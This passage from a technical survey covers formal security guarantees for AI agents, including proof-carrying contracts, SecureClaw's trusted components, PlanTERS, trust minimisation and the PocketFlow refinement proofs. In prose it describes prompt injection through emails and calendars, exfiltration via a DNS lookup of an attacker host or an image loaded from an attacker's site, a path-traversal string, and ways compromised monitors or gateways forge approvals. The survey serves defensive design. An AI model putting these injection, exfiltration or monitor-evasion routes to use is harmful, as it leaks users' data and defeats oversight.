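| **A2. Coverage** | A tool's model includes every state that a real call can pass through | A payment can go through twice after a timeout, but the model includes only one charge |
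| **A3. Initialisation and control** | The contract starts in a state that satisfies the clauses, and the Airlock's own steps keep it there | The Airlock starts closing the contract too late to meet the deadline |
| **A4. Execution integrity** | The Airlock runs the specified algorithm, and each call is the one whose proof it checked | Another program changes the payee after the check |
| **A5. Fidelity** | The Airlock's records remain a true description of the world | The records show 1,900 euros, but the provider has charged 2,100 |
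| **A6. Adequacy** | If the records are true and satisfy the clauses, the world is safe in the intended sense | The clauses limit hotel prices but omit fees |
| **A7. Isolation** | The agent acts only through the Airlock | The agent has its own copy of the payment password |

The first four assumptions imply that the recorded state satisfies the clauses at every moment. With A5 and A6, the actual state of the world satisfies them too. With A7, this result holds for any agent. An engineer can study each tool with no agent running, because isolation ensures that adding an agent, even a hostile one, creates no new effects while the tool runs.

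A3 is easy to overlook because it concerns the Airlock's own behaviour between calls. Ciliberto and colleagues describe a company that lets an agent run cloud computing jobs within a budget. The jobs keep costing money while the Airlock shuts them down, so the contract has to reserve enough for the shutdown:

bill + rate × shutdown time ≤ budget

Suppose the budget is 100 euros, the jobs cost 2 euros a minute, and a shutdown takes up to 3 minutes. The Airlock checks once a minute. When the bill is 92 euros, it can wait another minute, because one more minute and a shutdown would cost at most 8 euros. At 94 euros it must stop the jobs, and the final bill is at most 100 euros. If a shutdown can take 5 minutes, the bill could reach 104 euros because the model of the shutdown (A2) is wrong.

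A4 has a similar gap between theory and practice. The proof assumes each operation starts the moment the previous one ends, but a real computer pauses briefly in between. Ciliberto and colleagues set a maximum length for the pause and extend each tool's model to include whatever could change during it.

The guarantee needs isolation because the agent might otherwise pay people directly. Suppose the records show 1,900 euros of commitments and the agent makes a separate payment of 300. If the records don't change, they no longer describe the world, so A5 fails. If they change to 2,200, the clauses no longer hold. The engineer could extend every tool's model to include such payments, but then no call could have a valid proof, since the agent might overspend during any of them. The system would be safe, but it would block every call.

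Isolation is sufficient for the guarantee but not necessary. For example, if the agent had direct access to a card with a firm limit of 100 euros, the contract could count those 100 euros as spent from the start.

### From correct records to a safe world

The budget clause limits a number in the Airlock's records, but the family cares about what the payment provider actually charges. Ciliberto and colleagues connect the two through a ledger. Each payment j has three amounts: the reservation r_j in the ledger, the limit u_j that the provider has issued, and the total a_j that the provider has charged, including fees. The records are faithful if, for every payment,

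a_j ≤ u_j ≤ r_j

Adding up all the payments shows that the total charged is no more than the total reserved. The clause limits the total reserved to 2,000 euros, so the total charged is also at most 2,000 euros. This last step, called adequacy, needs only arithmetic here.

Fidelity takes more work because it depends on how two separate organisations behave:

- **The Airlock** must enter the reservation before it asks the provider for a payment, never lower or remove an entry, and be the only party that can request payments.
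- **The provider** must keep all charges for a payment, including fees and retries, within the limit, and must refuse charges that have no matching payment instruction.

The Airlock has to record a reservation before it sends a request, because a charge can arrive before the provider confirms the request. If it waited for a receipt before recording one, money could leave the account with no reservation to cover it. It also has to keep the reservation if the request times out, since the provider may have received the request anyway.

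Suppose the family's three nights have limits of 900, 500 and 500 euros, and the provider's small print allows charges of up to 10% over each limit. The ledger shows 1,900 euros, but the charges could reach 2,090, which would exceed the family's 2,000-euro budget even though every proof is valid. Reserving each limit plus 10% fixes this. The first two nights then reserve 1,540 euros, which leaves 460, so the third night's limit can be at most about 418 euros.

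Whether a record stays true also depends on what it means. If the hotel later cancels, "The booking service confirmed this room at noon" is still true, but "The hotel is holding this room" is now false. A digital signature on the confirmation proves who sent it, but the hotel could still give the room away. If the contract pays the travel agency when the rooms are secure, it needs the hotel's commitment to hold each room until a stated time, and it must check that this time hasn't passed.

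A proof of adequacy holds only for a particular formal definition of safety. In this example, "safe" means that charges through the payment provider stay within 2,000 euros. If the hotel collects a tourist tax in cash, the family may spend more than 2,000 euros without any assumption failing, because the definition leaves out cash. Somebody has to check the definition for such omissions.

### Who answers for each assumption

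Several of these conditions concern organisations that neither the family nor the travel agency controls. Ciliberto and colleagues propose that the parties go through the conditions before signing and decide how to support each one. Some conditions have a mathematical proof. For others, a named party commits to keeping the condition true, or the parties reduce the risk with tests and monitoring or openly accept it. The following table applies this to the travel contract.

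| Condition | Who answers for it | Support |
|---|---|---|
| The payment routine makes a reservation before it requests a payment | The routine's developer | Proof about the routine |
| Only the Airlock can use the payment password | The Airlock's operator | Review of who has access |
| Charges never exceed the limit | The payment provider | Commitment, with checks of its statements |
| The hotel holds a confirmed room until the stated time | The hotel | Commitment |
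| The clauses cover everything the family cares about | The family and the agency | Accepted risk |

Ciliberto and colleagues suggest deposits, insurance and automatic refunds. These commit someone to pay for a failure but aren't evidence that it won't happen, and a refund can't recall a passport scan sent to the wrong address. A contract needs stronger evidence than a promise when a condition protects secrets or other things that money can't restore.

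Responsibility for the invoice assistant's assumptions can be divided the same way. The accounts department would probably be responsible for those about which fields are sensitive, and the IT department for those about which programs can send email. If nobody assigns these responsibilities, the accounts department may add a field and assume that someone else is checking the gateway's rules.

### What the attacker can see

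Guarantees about leaks need further assumptions about what the attacker can observe. Dongol lists seven conditions that a deployed agent must meet before the theorems of the PlanTERS framework apply to it.

| Assumption | What must hold | What could break it |
|---|---|---|
| **Trusted execution** | A trusted interpreter runs the plan, and the model can't skip or change its steps | An agent that lets the model revise the plan after reading an email |
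| **Complete mediation** | The monitor rules on every tool call and every read of untrusted text, and never on two at once | A browser that the monitor doesn't control, or parallel calls that the monitor doesn't put in order |
| **Mediated reads** | Untrusted text reaches the model only after the monitor has allowed the read | A framework that adds new emails to the prompt automatically |
| **Silent denials** | A refused request has no effect that the attacker can see | An error message or log that the attacker can read |
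| **Limited observation** | The attacker can't see the monitor's state or the agent's internal steps | A reply on the user's screen that loads an image from the attacker's site |
| **Fresh sessions** | A new session clears everything the model keeps from untrusted text | A memory search that brings back text from old emails |
| **Trusted channels** | The attacker can't write to the sources of trusted inputs | A calendar that accepts outsiders' invitations |

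The condition on reads supports the fence theorem, which requires the monitor to revoke dangerous tools no later than the first untrusted read. If the framework puts an email into the prompt before the monitor acts, the model can follow instructions in the email while it still has those tools. The monitor would then revoke the tools too late, even though the plan and the monitor's rules look correct.

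When an assumption fails, the engineer can sometimes still use a weaker result. If the attacker can see refusals, Dongol has another attacker model that includes them, and the engineer can try to prove security under that model. If outsiders can write to the calendar, the engineer can reclassify it as untrusted. Reading the calendar may then become the first untrusted read, and if it does, the fence has to move earlier in the plan.

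A contract that covers a fully compromised model can't assume silent denials in the same way. In SecureClaw, the attacker controls the model and so sees every refusal it receives. Ma and Schmid therefore include policy decisions and refusal messages in what the attacker may learn.

### Checks on a live system

Ma and Schmid say the main risk of deploying SecureClaw is false assurance, since people may rely on the architecture even when a sensitive field is unmarked or an action can be carried out by a second route. They recommend keeping an inventory of the interfaces that carry out external actions and auditing the rules that identify sensitive fields.

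The best place to start an inventory of sinks is the outside service, because the agent's code shows only the routes that its developers remember. An email provider's settings usually list every password, key and connected application that can send messages. The engineer can revoke all of them except the executor's. After that, regularly comparing the provider's record of sent messages with the executor's record of accepted requests can expose a missed route, because a message sent through that route has no matching request. This comparison finds a violation only after the message has gone out, so it can't replace the inventory.

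The inventory should also include the company that runs the model. If the assistant uses a hosted model, that company receives every summary and every user request, even when the monitor checks every tool call. Ciliberto and colleagues recommend deciding whether the company is an intended recipient. If it isn't, the operator can run the model on its own machines or in a protected computing environment.

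**Outbound-network tests.** An engineer can run an ordinary test program where the driving loop runs and have it try to reach the outside. The test should use both IPv4 and IPv6 and cover direct connections to numeric addresses, internal company services, and name lookups, which are easy to forget. If a program looks up 4200.attacker.com, the query can reach the attacker's name server and reveal the number 4200, even if the firewall blocks all web traffic. The test also needs a control that should succeed, such as the same program on an open network, because a broken test program would make any network look isolated.

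The engineer has to test the network itself to check that the system is isolated, because a prompt can't establish isolation. An operator may tell the model that it is working in a simulation while a misconfigured network leaves the internet reachable.

The driving loop needs to reach only the model, the gateway and the executor. If the firewall is set to block everything else, any other connection that succeeds in a test is a fault. Repeating the test on a schedule can catch a setting that changes after the first check. The operator can also add a switch that halts the agent when a test fails, but this only limits the damage. If a halt takes 30 seconds, an agent that sends ten messages a second could send 300 before it stops.

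**Attestation.** Remote attestation lets someone check which software is running on another person's machine. Usually, a protected part of the hardware computes and signs a fingerprint of the loaded program, and the remote party compares it with the fingerprint of the version it has reviewed. In proof-carrying contracts, both parties do this before they sign the contract, so they don't have to trust whoever hosts the Airlock. Attestation supports the assumption that the right program is running, but it doesn't show that the program is free of bugs, that the firewall has the right settings, or that the payment provider respects its limits.

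**Re-checking after changes.** An assumption that held at launch can fail later even if the agent doesn't change. In the website-testing example, the contract's compiler translates domain names into numeric addresses, but a domain's owner can point it to a different address at any time. David and colleagues keep each translation for a declared period and require the engineer to check again if the address later changes. For payments, Ciliberto and colleagues suggest recording which conditions each argument uses, so that when a provider changes its access rules, the engineer can find every contract that depended on the old ones.

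For the invoice assistant, the contract could list the changes that trigger a new check.

| Change | What to check again |
|---|---|
| The invoice form gets a new field | Whether the gateway marks it correctly |
| The assistant gets a new tool | Whether the tool opens another route to the outside, and whether approvals include every field that affects what it does |
| The email service adds a forwarding option | Whether the approved request still determines who receives the message |
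| An administrator restores the executor from a backup | Whether the restored record is missing recently used approvals |
| The company moves the model to another provider | Whether the new provider may receive the summaries, and whether the firewall still blocks everything else |

The table doesn't include replacing the model with a newer one on the same machines, because none of the assumptions behind these guarantees is about how the model behaves.

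## Working out what fails when a trusted component is compromised

SecureClaw's guarantees rely on four trusted components, and an attacker may take over one of them. The last part of a contract, the degradation table, lists the guarantees that fail in each case. Engineers can use it to decide what to harden first, and after a break-in the company can use it to work out which guarantees still hold. To fill in a component's row, the engineer assumes the attacker has everything the component holds and can call every interface it can call, then looks for a way to violate each guarantee.

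### SecureClaw, one component at a time

An attacker who controls the gateway receives every invoice in its raw form and can copy it to the model's side, so the data guarantee fails. The action guarantee also fails, because the policy engine in Ma and Schmid's protocol approves a fingerprint that the gateway supplies. The attacker can show the policy engine a harmless email to approver@corp.com together with the fingerprint of an email to an outside address. The policy engine can't detect the mismatch because it doesn't hold the binding key needed to recompute the fingerprint. At commit, the executor finds a genuine approval that matches the harmful email and sends that email.

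The executor's own checks still work in this case, so Ma and Schmid describe the damage as undermining the meaning of request binding. But those checks offer little protection when the attacker chooses what each approval stands for. If the policy engine computed the fingerprint itself, the attacker could no longer swap requests. The attacker could still name the wrong caller, so callers would also have to sign their requests.

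The data store holds the raw invoices, so the data guarantee also fails if the store is compromised. The effect on actions is harder to state. Suppose the policy engine approves an email with version 3 of an invoice. The executor looks up the handle and sends whatever the store returns, which could be an invoice with a different bank account, or the payroll file. The request's fingerprint still matches because it covers the handle and version number but not the text. Ma and Schmid say only that the integrity of lookups may fail "unless separately protected".

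If the action guarantee were only that no email goes to an unapproved address, this wouldn't break it. But the assistant's contract also promises that each email contains the approved version of the invoice, and that promise fails. To protect it, the gateway can add a fingerprint of the invoice's text to the approved request, and the executor can recompute the fingerprint before sending. The fingerprint needs its own secret key, because otherwise the untrusted side could use it to test guesses about the invoice amount.

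An attacker who controls the policy engine can approve any action, so the action guarantee fails. The attacker also sees whatever the gateway submits for a decision. The data guarantee still holds as long as those submissions contain no raw invoice text, because the model's side receives only handles and summaries. However, the attacker can approve an email that sends the invoice to their own address. The executor refuses to send it if the handle's record doesn't permit that destination, but it won't block the email if the handle permits every destination.

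The executor has the connection to the email service, so an attacker who controls it can send emails without approval. The executor can also look up handles, which exposes invoices. A stricter store could require an approval before each lookup, but this wouldn't help if approvals used message authentication codes, because the key that checks a tag can also make one. With digital signatures, the executor would hold only a public key for checking approvals, so the attacker could fetch only the invoices that the policy engine had approved for sending. The policy engine's log would still be intact, and comparing it with the email provider's record would expose the unapproved emails.

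| Attacker controls | Action guarantee | Data guarantee |
|---|---|---|
| Model and driving loop | Holds | Holds, apart from declared releases |
| Gateway | Fails: an approval can stand for a different request | Fails: the gateway receives the raw invoices |
| Data store | Approved recipients only, but the invoice may be wrong unless the executor can check its text | Fails: the store holds the raw invoices |
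| Policy engine | Fails: the attacker can approve any request | Holds for the model's side, if requests contain no raw invoice text |
| Executor | Fails: the attacker can send email without approval | Fails: the executor can look up invoices |

The rows describe roles, but attackers break into machines and accounts, so a contract should also have rows for shared machines, databases and administrator accounts. A row for the single workstation in Ma and Schmid's experiments would show both guarantees failing. Similarly, if the executor keeps its record of used approvals in the same database as the invoices, an attacker there can delete an entry and resubmit an old payment, provided its approval hasn't expired.

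### The weakest trust that is enough

The table considers one component at a time. It doesn't show whether attacks that need two compromised components matter, or whether a shorter list of trusted components would be enough. *Trust a Few* (Mittal and Thakkar, 2026) answers this kind of question for security protocols, where the assumptions concern keys, values and communication channels.

In Mittal and Thakkar's main example, B wants to confirm that A is taking part right now. B sends a random number N, and A signs N together with both names and returns the signature. The three assumptions that might matter are that A's signing key is secret, that B's signing key is secret, and that N is fresh, meaning nobody has used it before. Mittal and Thakkar list three attacks and each one's stopping set, which contains every assumption that would rule out the attack by itself.

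| Attack | What happens | Stopping set |
|---|---|---|
| Forgery | The attacker has A's key and signs N | A's key is secret |
| Replay | B reuses an old N, and the attacker resends A's old signature | N is fresh |
| Double forgery | The attacker forges A's signature and, in a second session, B's signature too | A's key is secret; B's key is secret |

A set of assumptions is sufficient if it contains at least one member of every stopping set. Here, a sufficient set must include the assumptions that A's key is secret and that N is fresh. Those two assumptions also stop the double forgery, so B's key doesn't have to be secret for this goal.

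The double forgery is redundant because its stopping set contains the forgery's. Mittal and Thakkar call an attack minimal if its stopping set doesn't contain another attack's smaller one. They prove that the weakest sufficient sets of assumptions are exactly the minimal hitting sets of the minimal attacks' stopping sets. A hitting set includes at least one assumption from each of these stopping sets, and it is minimal if removing any assumption would leave it with none from at least one of them.

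The result holds because a set of assumptions fails if some attack remains possible, and an attack remains possible exactly when the set contains no assumption from that attack's stopping set. Redundant attacks make no difference, because a set that contains an assumption from a smaller stopping set also contains one from every larger stopping set that includes it.

There can be more than one weakest set. In a variant of the protocol, A and B share two keys, and A encrypts the reply with one key and then with the other. A forger needs both keys, so the designer can rely on a fresh N and the secrecy of either key. Mittal and Thakkar prove that a single weakest set exists exactly when every minimal attack has only one stopping assumption. The condition must be limited to minimal attacks, because the signed protocol has a single weakest set even though the double forgery has two stopping assumptions.

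A single search for attacks can miss some. If the designer assumes nothing, a standard protocol analyser finds the forgery and stops, because a forged signature is enough to explain everything B receives. The replay appears only after the designer assumes that A's key is secret. Mittal and Thakkar therefore use a loop that proposes a smallest set of assumptions that rules out all known attacks, uses a verifier to search for an attack that still works under those assumptions, and repeats. The signed protocol takes three queries, compared with eight for checking every combination of assumptions.

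### From keys to components

Applying the theorem to SecureClaw's components goes beyond Mittal and Thakkar's paper. This is valid if trusting one more component only removes possible runs of the system, and they point out that the hitting-set form follows from this condition alone. Components satisfy it because a fully corrupted component can also behave honestly, so trusting the gateway only removes the runs in which it misbehaves. The stopping set of an attack is the set of components that misbehave in it.

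The design has to stay fixed while the list of trusted components varies. If engineers removed the executor's check on the invoice text because they trusted the data store, the system could do things it couldn't before, and the theorem would no longer apply.

The gateway, the data store and the executor can each break the data guarantee alone by leaking an invoice. The minimal attacks therefore have the stopping sets {gateway}, {store} and {executor}, and the weakest trust assumption includes all three. For the action guarantee, the stopping sets are {gateway}, {policy engine} and {executor}, so those three must be trustworthy. If that guarantee covers the text of the invoice and the executor can't check the text, {store} is also a stopping set. An attack that uses both the gateway and the policy engine adds no trust requirement, because the gateway is enough by itself.

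The theorem also shows how limiting destinations affects the broader promise that no outsider receives an invoice. If handles permit every destination, a compromised policy engine can break this promise by itself, so the engine belongs in the weakest trust. If handles permit only corp.com addresses, the attacker must also change the handle's record in the store. That attack's stopping set, {policy engine, store}, is redundant because it contains {store}. The promise therefore no longer depends on the policy engine, again provided that the engine receives no raw invoice text.

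Errors that the policy allows have an empty stopping set. A hijacked model can email the wrong colleague while all four components work correctly, so trusting more components can't help. Mittal and Thakkar describe a similar case in Kerberos, a widely used login system. In 2005, researchers found that an insider could relay a client's request and learn the session keys without stealing any honest party's key, so no assumption about keys would have ruled out the attack.

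A list of known attacks can prove that each component on it must be trusted, but not that trusting those components is enough, because someone may have missed an attack. Proving that requires security theorems, and Ma and Schmid's theorems assume that all four components are trusted. Before dropping the policy engine from the data guarantee's list, an engineer should check that the proof never relies on the engine being honest.

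### Two evaluators that share one decision

An ordinary policy engine has access to every request, including who is emailing whom. SecureClaw can optionally split the engine into two evaluators and hide these details from each one. It does this using private information retrieval, which lets a client look up a database entry without revealing which one, and secure multi-party computation, which lets several servers compute a result without revealing their inputs to each other.

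In a textbook version of private retrieval, two servers hold the same list of eight policy bits, where 1 means "allow", and the gateway wants the third bit. It sends the first server a random set of positions, say {1, 3, 6}, and sends the second server the same set with position 3 switched, {1, 6}. Each server adds up the bits at its positions and replies "odd" or "even". If the replies differ, the third bit is 1. Each server sees only a random set, which reveals nothing about the position the gateway wants. But if the servers compare their sets, they can see that only position 3 differs and learn which bit the gateway wanted.

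Ma and Schmid's fifth theorem limits what one evaluator can learn. The attacker chooses two actions, the system processes one of them once, and the attacker sees everything that one evaluator sees. The attacker can't tell which action was processed if both have the same permitted leakage. The permitted leakage includes the database and program used, the batch size, whether the action needs confirmation, and roughly when it happened. The proof replaces the retrieval messages with simulated ones, then does the same for the joint computation.

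The theorem doesn't rule out an evaluator learning whether a payment is above $5,000 if payments above that amount need confirmation. It covers only single actions, not patterns across many, and it assumes that both evaluators follow the protocol and don't collude. Private evaluation was also slower in Ma and Schmid's local measurements, where policy checks took an average of 149 milliseconds with two evaluators and 15 with one ordinary engine, excluding any network delay between separate servers.

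The split does not protect authorization. In the textbook example, a malicious server can reply "odd" instead of "even", which turns a 0 into a 1, and so a refusal into an approval. SecureClaw's executor checks an authentication code on each evaluator's share of the decision, but the code shows only who sent the share, not whether they computed it correctly. Ma and Schmid therefore do not guarantee authorization if either evaluator is malicious. Two stopping sets, {first evaluator} and {second evaluator}, have replaced {policy engine}, so the weakest trust assumption must now include both evaluators.

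### Two independent approvals

A hypothetical alternative uses two complete policy engines with separate keys, and an executor that requires an approval from each. An attacker has to control both engines to get a forbidden request approved. This attack has the stopping set {first engine, second engine}, just like the forgery in the two-key protocol, so one honest engine is enough to stop it. The drawbacks are that either engine can block all work by withholding its approvals, and both see every request in full.

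Suppose each engine or evaluator has a 2% chance of being compromised in a year, independently of the others. The table also includes a design that requires approval from any two of three engines.

| Design | Chance that an attacker can approve forbidden requests | Chance that an attacker can block all work | Who sees full requests |
|---|---|---|---|
| One engine | 2% | 2% | The engine |
| Two evaluators sharing a decision | 4% | 4% | Neither evaluator alone |
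| Two approvals required | 0.04% | 4% | Both engines |
| Two of three approvals required | 0.12% | 0.12% | All three engines |

A compromised gateway or executor can still break authorization on its own. If each also has a 2% chance of compromise, the total chance that authorization fails is 5.9% with one engine, 7.8% with two evaluators and 4.0% with two approvals. Once the executor requires two approvals, hardening the gateway and the executor is more worthwhile than adding a third engine, at least for preventing forbidden actions.

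Independence is also easy to lose. If both engines load their rules from the same server, an attacker who controls that server can change both sets of rules. The server is then the only member of a stopping set, and the second engine adds no protection against that attack. Running the same software on both engines creates a similar weakness, because one bug may let an attacker into both.

### When a component fails during a run

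The degradation table treats a compromised component as hostile from the start. In practice, a component usually works correctly until a particular input triggers a bug. *When Good Components Go Bad* (Abate, Azevedo de Amorim et al., 2018) formalizes this for languages such as C, where writing past the end of an array can give an attacker control. A component keeps its guarantees until such a bug occurs. After that, the attacker controls the component but can use only the privileges it already had.

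They illustrate this with a program that has three components. The first reads and parses a request from outside. The second processes the request, calls the third to check that the reply is valid, and then sends the reply. The parsing code may have a bug that some requests trigger. An attacker could exploit a different weakness in the second component by calling it before its set-up routine has run.

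If a malicious request takes over the first component, the attacker can invent requests, so replies no longer correspond to real ones. The replies are still valid, because the second component still calls the check. The first component runs the set-up routine before it reads any request, so the attacker gains control too late to skip it. An analysis that treated the first component as hostile from the start would have to assume that the attacker could skip the routine and take over the second component as well.

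Abate and colleagues make this precise with a replacement game. They take a finite record of what the compiled program did and try to reproduce it from the source code. Whenever a component triggers a bug, they replace it with an arbitrary component that has the same interface and start again, until they reproduce the whole record. A programmer can therefore reason about source code in which hostile components replace the compromised ones, without studying the compiler or the machine. They used the proof assistant Coq to prove that a compiler for a small language supports this reasoning.

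In SecureClaw, the gateway is probably the component most exposed to this kind of attack, because it processes files that outsiders wrote. Suppose an attacker uses a malformed invoice to take over the gateway at noon. The emails sent before noon all had proper approvals, and the attacker can't change that. But if the gateway can read old invoices from the data store, the attacker can still steal secrets from invoices that arrived months ago. The engineer can reduce this loss by letting the gateway add invoices to the store but not read them.

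Abate and colleagues also improve their example by moving all reading, checking and sending into one simple component and leaving the complicated processing to components without those privileges. Both properties then hold even if the attacker takes over the other two components. For SecureClaw, an engineer could similarly move file parsing out of the gateway into a component that has no keys and no role in building requests, and start a fresh copy of it for each file. An attacker who sent a malicious invoice would then take over a component that holds only that invoice, whose contents the attacker already knows.

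### Stolen keys

An attacker may also steal a key without taking over the component that uses it. *From Dolev-Yao to Strong Adaptive Corruption* (Basin and Cremers, 2009) formalises a hierarchy of such attackers for security protocols. The weakest controls the network but can't break the cryptography, and stronger ones can also read parts of a participant's memory during a run. Their later paper, *Know Your Enemy*, combines separate rules for different kinds of compromise and adds the resulting attackers to Scyther, a tool for analysing protocols. According to Mittal and Thakkar, these rules distinguish long-term keys, session keys and random values, and can depend on whether a long-term key leaks before or after a session ends.

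SecureClaw's table could make similar distinctions, because its keys aren't equally dangerous to lose:

- **Approval key:** the action guarantee fails. The attacker can preview a forbidden email, receive a record that contains its fingerprint and the decision "deny", change the decision to "allow", and compute a new authentication code.
- **Binding key:** the attacker can compute fingerprints, but still needs two different requests with the same one. For a 256-bit fingerprint, finding such a pair takes about 2^128 attempts. The action guarantee therefore holds in practice, although its proof would need a different assumption about the hash function.
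- **Handle key:** the attacker can compute valid handles if the gateway's nonces are predictable, for example because they come from a counter. The executor's limits on callers, sessions and destinations still apply.

If an attacker steals the policy engine's approval key and engineers repair the engine without replacing the key, the attacker can still forge approvals with current timestamps. The contract should therefore list, for each component, the keys that the company must replace before it can rely on the guarantees again.

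## Carrying the proof from the model to the running code

The guarantees and the degradation table describe a design, and the code a company runs may not match it. Suppose the code that puts SecureClaw's requests into their fixed format left out the blind-copy field. An attacker could get approval for an email to approver@corp.com and then add an outside address as a hidden recipient. The main theorem of Ma and Schmid would still be true, but it wouldn't apply to this code, because it assumes that the request includes every field that affects the outcome.

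### Three levels of proof

A pen-and-paper proof is about a design, and people check it by reading it. A mechanised proof expresses the design as formal definitions, and software checks every step. With verified code, the proof also covers the program itself, or at least the source code it is compiled from.

| System | What a program has checked | What connects the proof to a deployment |
|---|---|---|
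| SecureClaw | Nothing: the theorems are on paper | Tests of the code |
| Alignment contracts | The core theorems about the monitor, in Lean 4 | The assumption that every effect reaches the monitor as a correct event |
| PlanTERS | The theory and the verdicts on 25 example agents, in Isabelle/HOL | Seven assumptions about the deployed agent |
| Proof-carrying contracts | The theory, in Lean 4, and a new proof for every call | Assumptions about the Airlock, the tools and outside services |
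| Containment Verification | The theory and the main loop of one agent framework, in Dafny | A compiler, some unverified code around the loop, and effect exclusivity |

Mechanising a proof catches mistakes in the reasoning and makes the author write down every premise. It doesn't check whether the premises are true of a real system. As David and colleagues explain, Lean checks that a monitor applying their five clauses admits only permitted traces, but it can't check that a hook in an operating system reports every connection.

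PlanTERS is mechanised in about 31,600 lines of Isabelle across 89 files. Its 25 agents are small test cases, each built to isolate one mechanism, such as a fence or an approval. The Call Approval agent is secure against an attacker that can't measure timing, but Dongol proved that the standard proof method can never show this. Dongol also developed two new methods for such cases. A failed proof attempt therefore doesn't necessarily mean that there is a leak.

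Proof-carrying contracts use Lean for the general theorems and again at run time, when the Airlock checks the proof for each call. These run-time checks don't verify the Airlock's own software, so Ciliberto and colleagues still have to assume that it follows the algorithm in their model.

That assumption can fail even when a team takes verification seriously. Category Labs' *finding bugs that frontier models miss* uses a feature of the Monad blockchain to show what a design-level proof can miss when the code diverges from the model. For another feature, a proof about the C++ code itself exposed undefined behaviour, where the language doesn't specify what the program will do, that an ordinary review by the AI model Claude had missed.

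### Refinement, one step at a time

Engineers usually connect a model to code by refinement. They prove a property of a simple abstract model, then show that the abstract model can do anything the detailed system does. Moon and Varshney apply refinement to PocketFlow, the small agent framework in which they model the AI by havoc, meaning that it can choose any action at every step.

Both models have a starting state and a rule for the possible steps. In each step, the system receives an action from the AI, emits an event such as "file read", and moves to a new state. If it refuses the action, it emits an event that stands for no effect.

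Suppose an agent may read only files under /workspace. The abstract state needs little more than a list of the files read so far. The concrete state also includes a real program's bookkeeping, such as a history and a flag for whether the loop has halted. A matching relation pairs each concrete state with an abstract one by dropping the bookkeeping, and another relation pairs concrete events with abstract ones.

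The engineer then proves three conditions:

- **Start:** the two starting states match.
- **Step:** if two states match and the concrete system can take a step for some action, the abstract model can take a step for the same action. The two events match, and so do the two new states.
- **Policy:** if the abstract step obeys the abstract policy, the matching concrete step obeys the concrete policy.

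The engineer also proves that the abstract model obeys its policy for every possible sequence of actions. The soundness theorem then states that every step of the concrete system obeys the concrete policy, whatever strategy the AI follows. The proof is by induction:

1. Take any strategy and any run of the concrete system that it produces. The starting states match.
2. Suppose the states still match after i steps. By the step condition, the abstract model can take the next step with the same action, and the states match after i + 1 steps.
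3. Continuing in this way builds an abstract run with exactly the same actions. The abstract model is safe for all sequences of actions, so it is safe for this one.
4. By the policy condition, each step of the concrete run is safe too.

If a hijacked AI model requests /etc/passwd, a correct loop blocks the request, and so does the abstract model. If a bug let the request through, the concrete system would emit a "file read" event that the abstract model can't match. The step condition would then be false, and Dafny would reject the proof.

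The step condition covers every pair of matching states, including some that never occur, such as one in which the step counter is already far over its limit. To exclude these, the engineer adds an invariant, a condition that holds at the start and that every step preserves. PocketFlow's invariant includes the rule that the history's length agrees with the step counter. Finding a suitable invariant is often the hardest part of such a proof.

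The same method would suit SecureClaw's executor. In the abstract model, the executor sends a payment and marks its approval as used in one step, but real code needs two. Let a state of the code match a state of the model if every approval used in the model is marked in the executor's record. Code that marks first and sends second meets this condition, because the approval is already in the record when the payment goes out. If the code sends first, there is a point when the model has used the approval but the record has no mark, so the states don't match and the proof fails. A crash at that point would let an attacker submit the payment again.

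Refinement of this kind preserves rules about single steps, but it can lose secrecy. Suppose the abstract gateway may answer a refused request with either of two messages. Code that sends one message for invoices above $5,000 and the other for the rest satisfies the step condition, because the abstract model permits both. But the attacker can then tell from the message whether the invoice exceeds $5,000. For a data guarantee, the engineer has to remove such choices from the abstract model or compare two runs of the code directly.

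### What the PocketFlow proof covers

PocketFlow represents an agent as a graph of nodes, and its main loop moves from one node to the next according to the action that the current node emits. The verified version has four types of action and enforces three limits:

- The agent reads files only under the workspace folder.
- It calls only tools on an approved list.
- It takes no more than a set number of steps.

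A pipeline of Claude models wrote the specifications and proofs for two agents, one that reads files and one that retrieves documents to answer questions. Dafny checked each path through the graphs in 1.2 to 2.5 seconds. Writing the proofs took much longer than checking them, and each run of the pipeline used between 1.6 and 3.4 million tokens. When a proof fails, the pipeline is allowed to change only the proof file, so it can't weaken the theorem to make the proof succeed.

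These limits are modest compared with the invoice assistant's contract. The tool rule only checks whether a tool is on the list, so if the list includes an email tool, the agent can email anyone. The file rule requires each path to start with the name of the workspace folder. If the check only compares characters, /workspace/../payroll.csv passes, even though the operating system would open a file outside the folder. Moon and Varshney also haven't tried the method on a larger framework with dozens of action types, where the proof would have many more cases.

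After all this, the following still has to be right:

- **The policy.** Dafny can't tell whether the three limits are the ones the company needs.
- **The matching relations.** A relation that paired a real "email sent" event with "no effect" could hide a violation.
- **The entry point.** Unverified code parses the model's text and turns it into one of the four actions.
- **The exits.** Under effect exclusivity, the agent has no way to affect the outside world except through the verified loop.
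- **The tools.** Dafny's verifier checks the proof, and its compiler translates the verified source into Python.
- **Everything below.** The model leaves out concurrency, timing and hardware, and no proof covers the Python interpreter.

The guarantee applies to the Python code that Dafny generates, so it does not cover the original PocketFlow package, which contains different code. Moon and Varshney tested the Dafny-generated code with both permitted and forbidden actions, and it recorded only the permitted ones.

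### Proofs that succeed and mean nothing

A proof checker confirms that a statement follows from its assumptions, even if the statement is trivial. *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems* (Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues, 2017) describes an example in Chapar, a verified system that stores copies of data on several servers. In a sample program, one user uploads a photo and then posts "Uploaded". Anyone who sees the post should also be able to see the photo. After finding the post, the program was supposed to check for the photo, but it checked for the post again. That check always succeeded, so it could not detect a missing photo.

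Such a statement is vacuous, meaning it is true for reasons unrelated to the system's safety. A theorem whose assumptions contradict each other is vacuous because no system satisfies them all. A rule about every email in a log is also vacuous if the model of the system never adds emails to the log.

The risk grows when a language model writes the specification. If the model can read the code, it may describe what the code does, bugs included, and the proof will succeed for any code. Moon and Varshney therefore use an information barrier. The step that writes the safety property receives a template and a description of the framework's interface, but none of the implementation. A later step can read the code but can't change the property.

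They express this as zero mutual information between the property and the implementation, given the interface description, the template and the model's weights. The weights may already contain information about the implementation, because PocketFlow's code has been public since 2024 and the model may have learned it in training. The barrier blocks copying from the prompt, which is probably the larger danger, but it can't remove what is already in the weights.

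The pipeline then applies three gates, two of which sabotage the proof on purpose.

| Gate | What the pipeline does | Result needed to pass |
|---|---|---|
| Resolution | Parses and type-checks the Dafny code, within 30 seconds | The code is well formed |
| Vacuity | Reduces the invariant to a basic format check and deletes the proofs of the lemmas | Verification fails |
| Discrimination | Has a language model insert a plausible mistake into the proof file | Verification fails |

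If the sabotaged version still verified, the specification would be too weak to demand a real proof.

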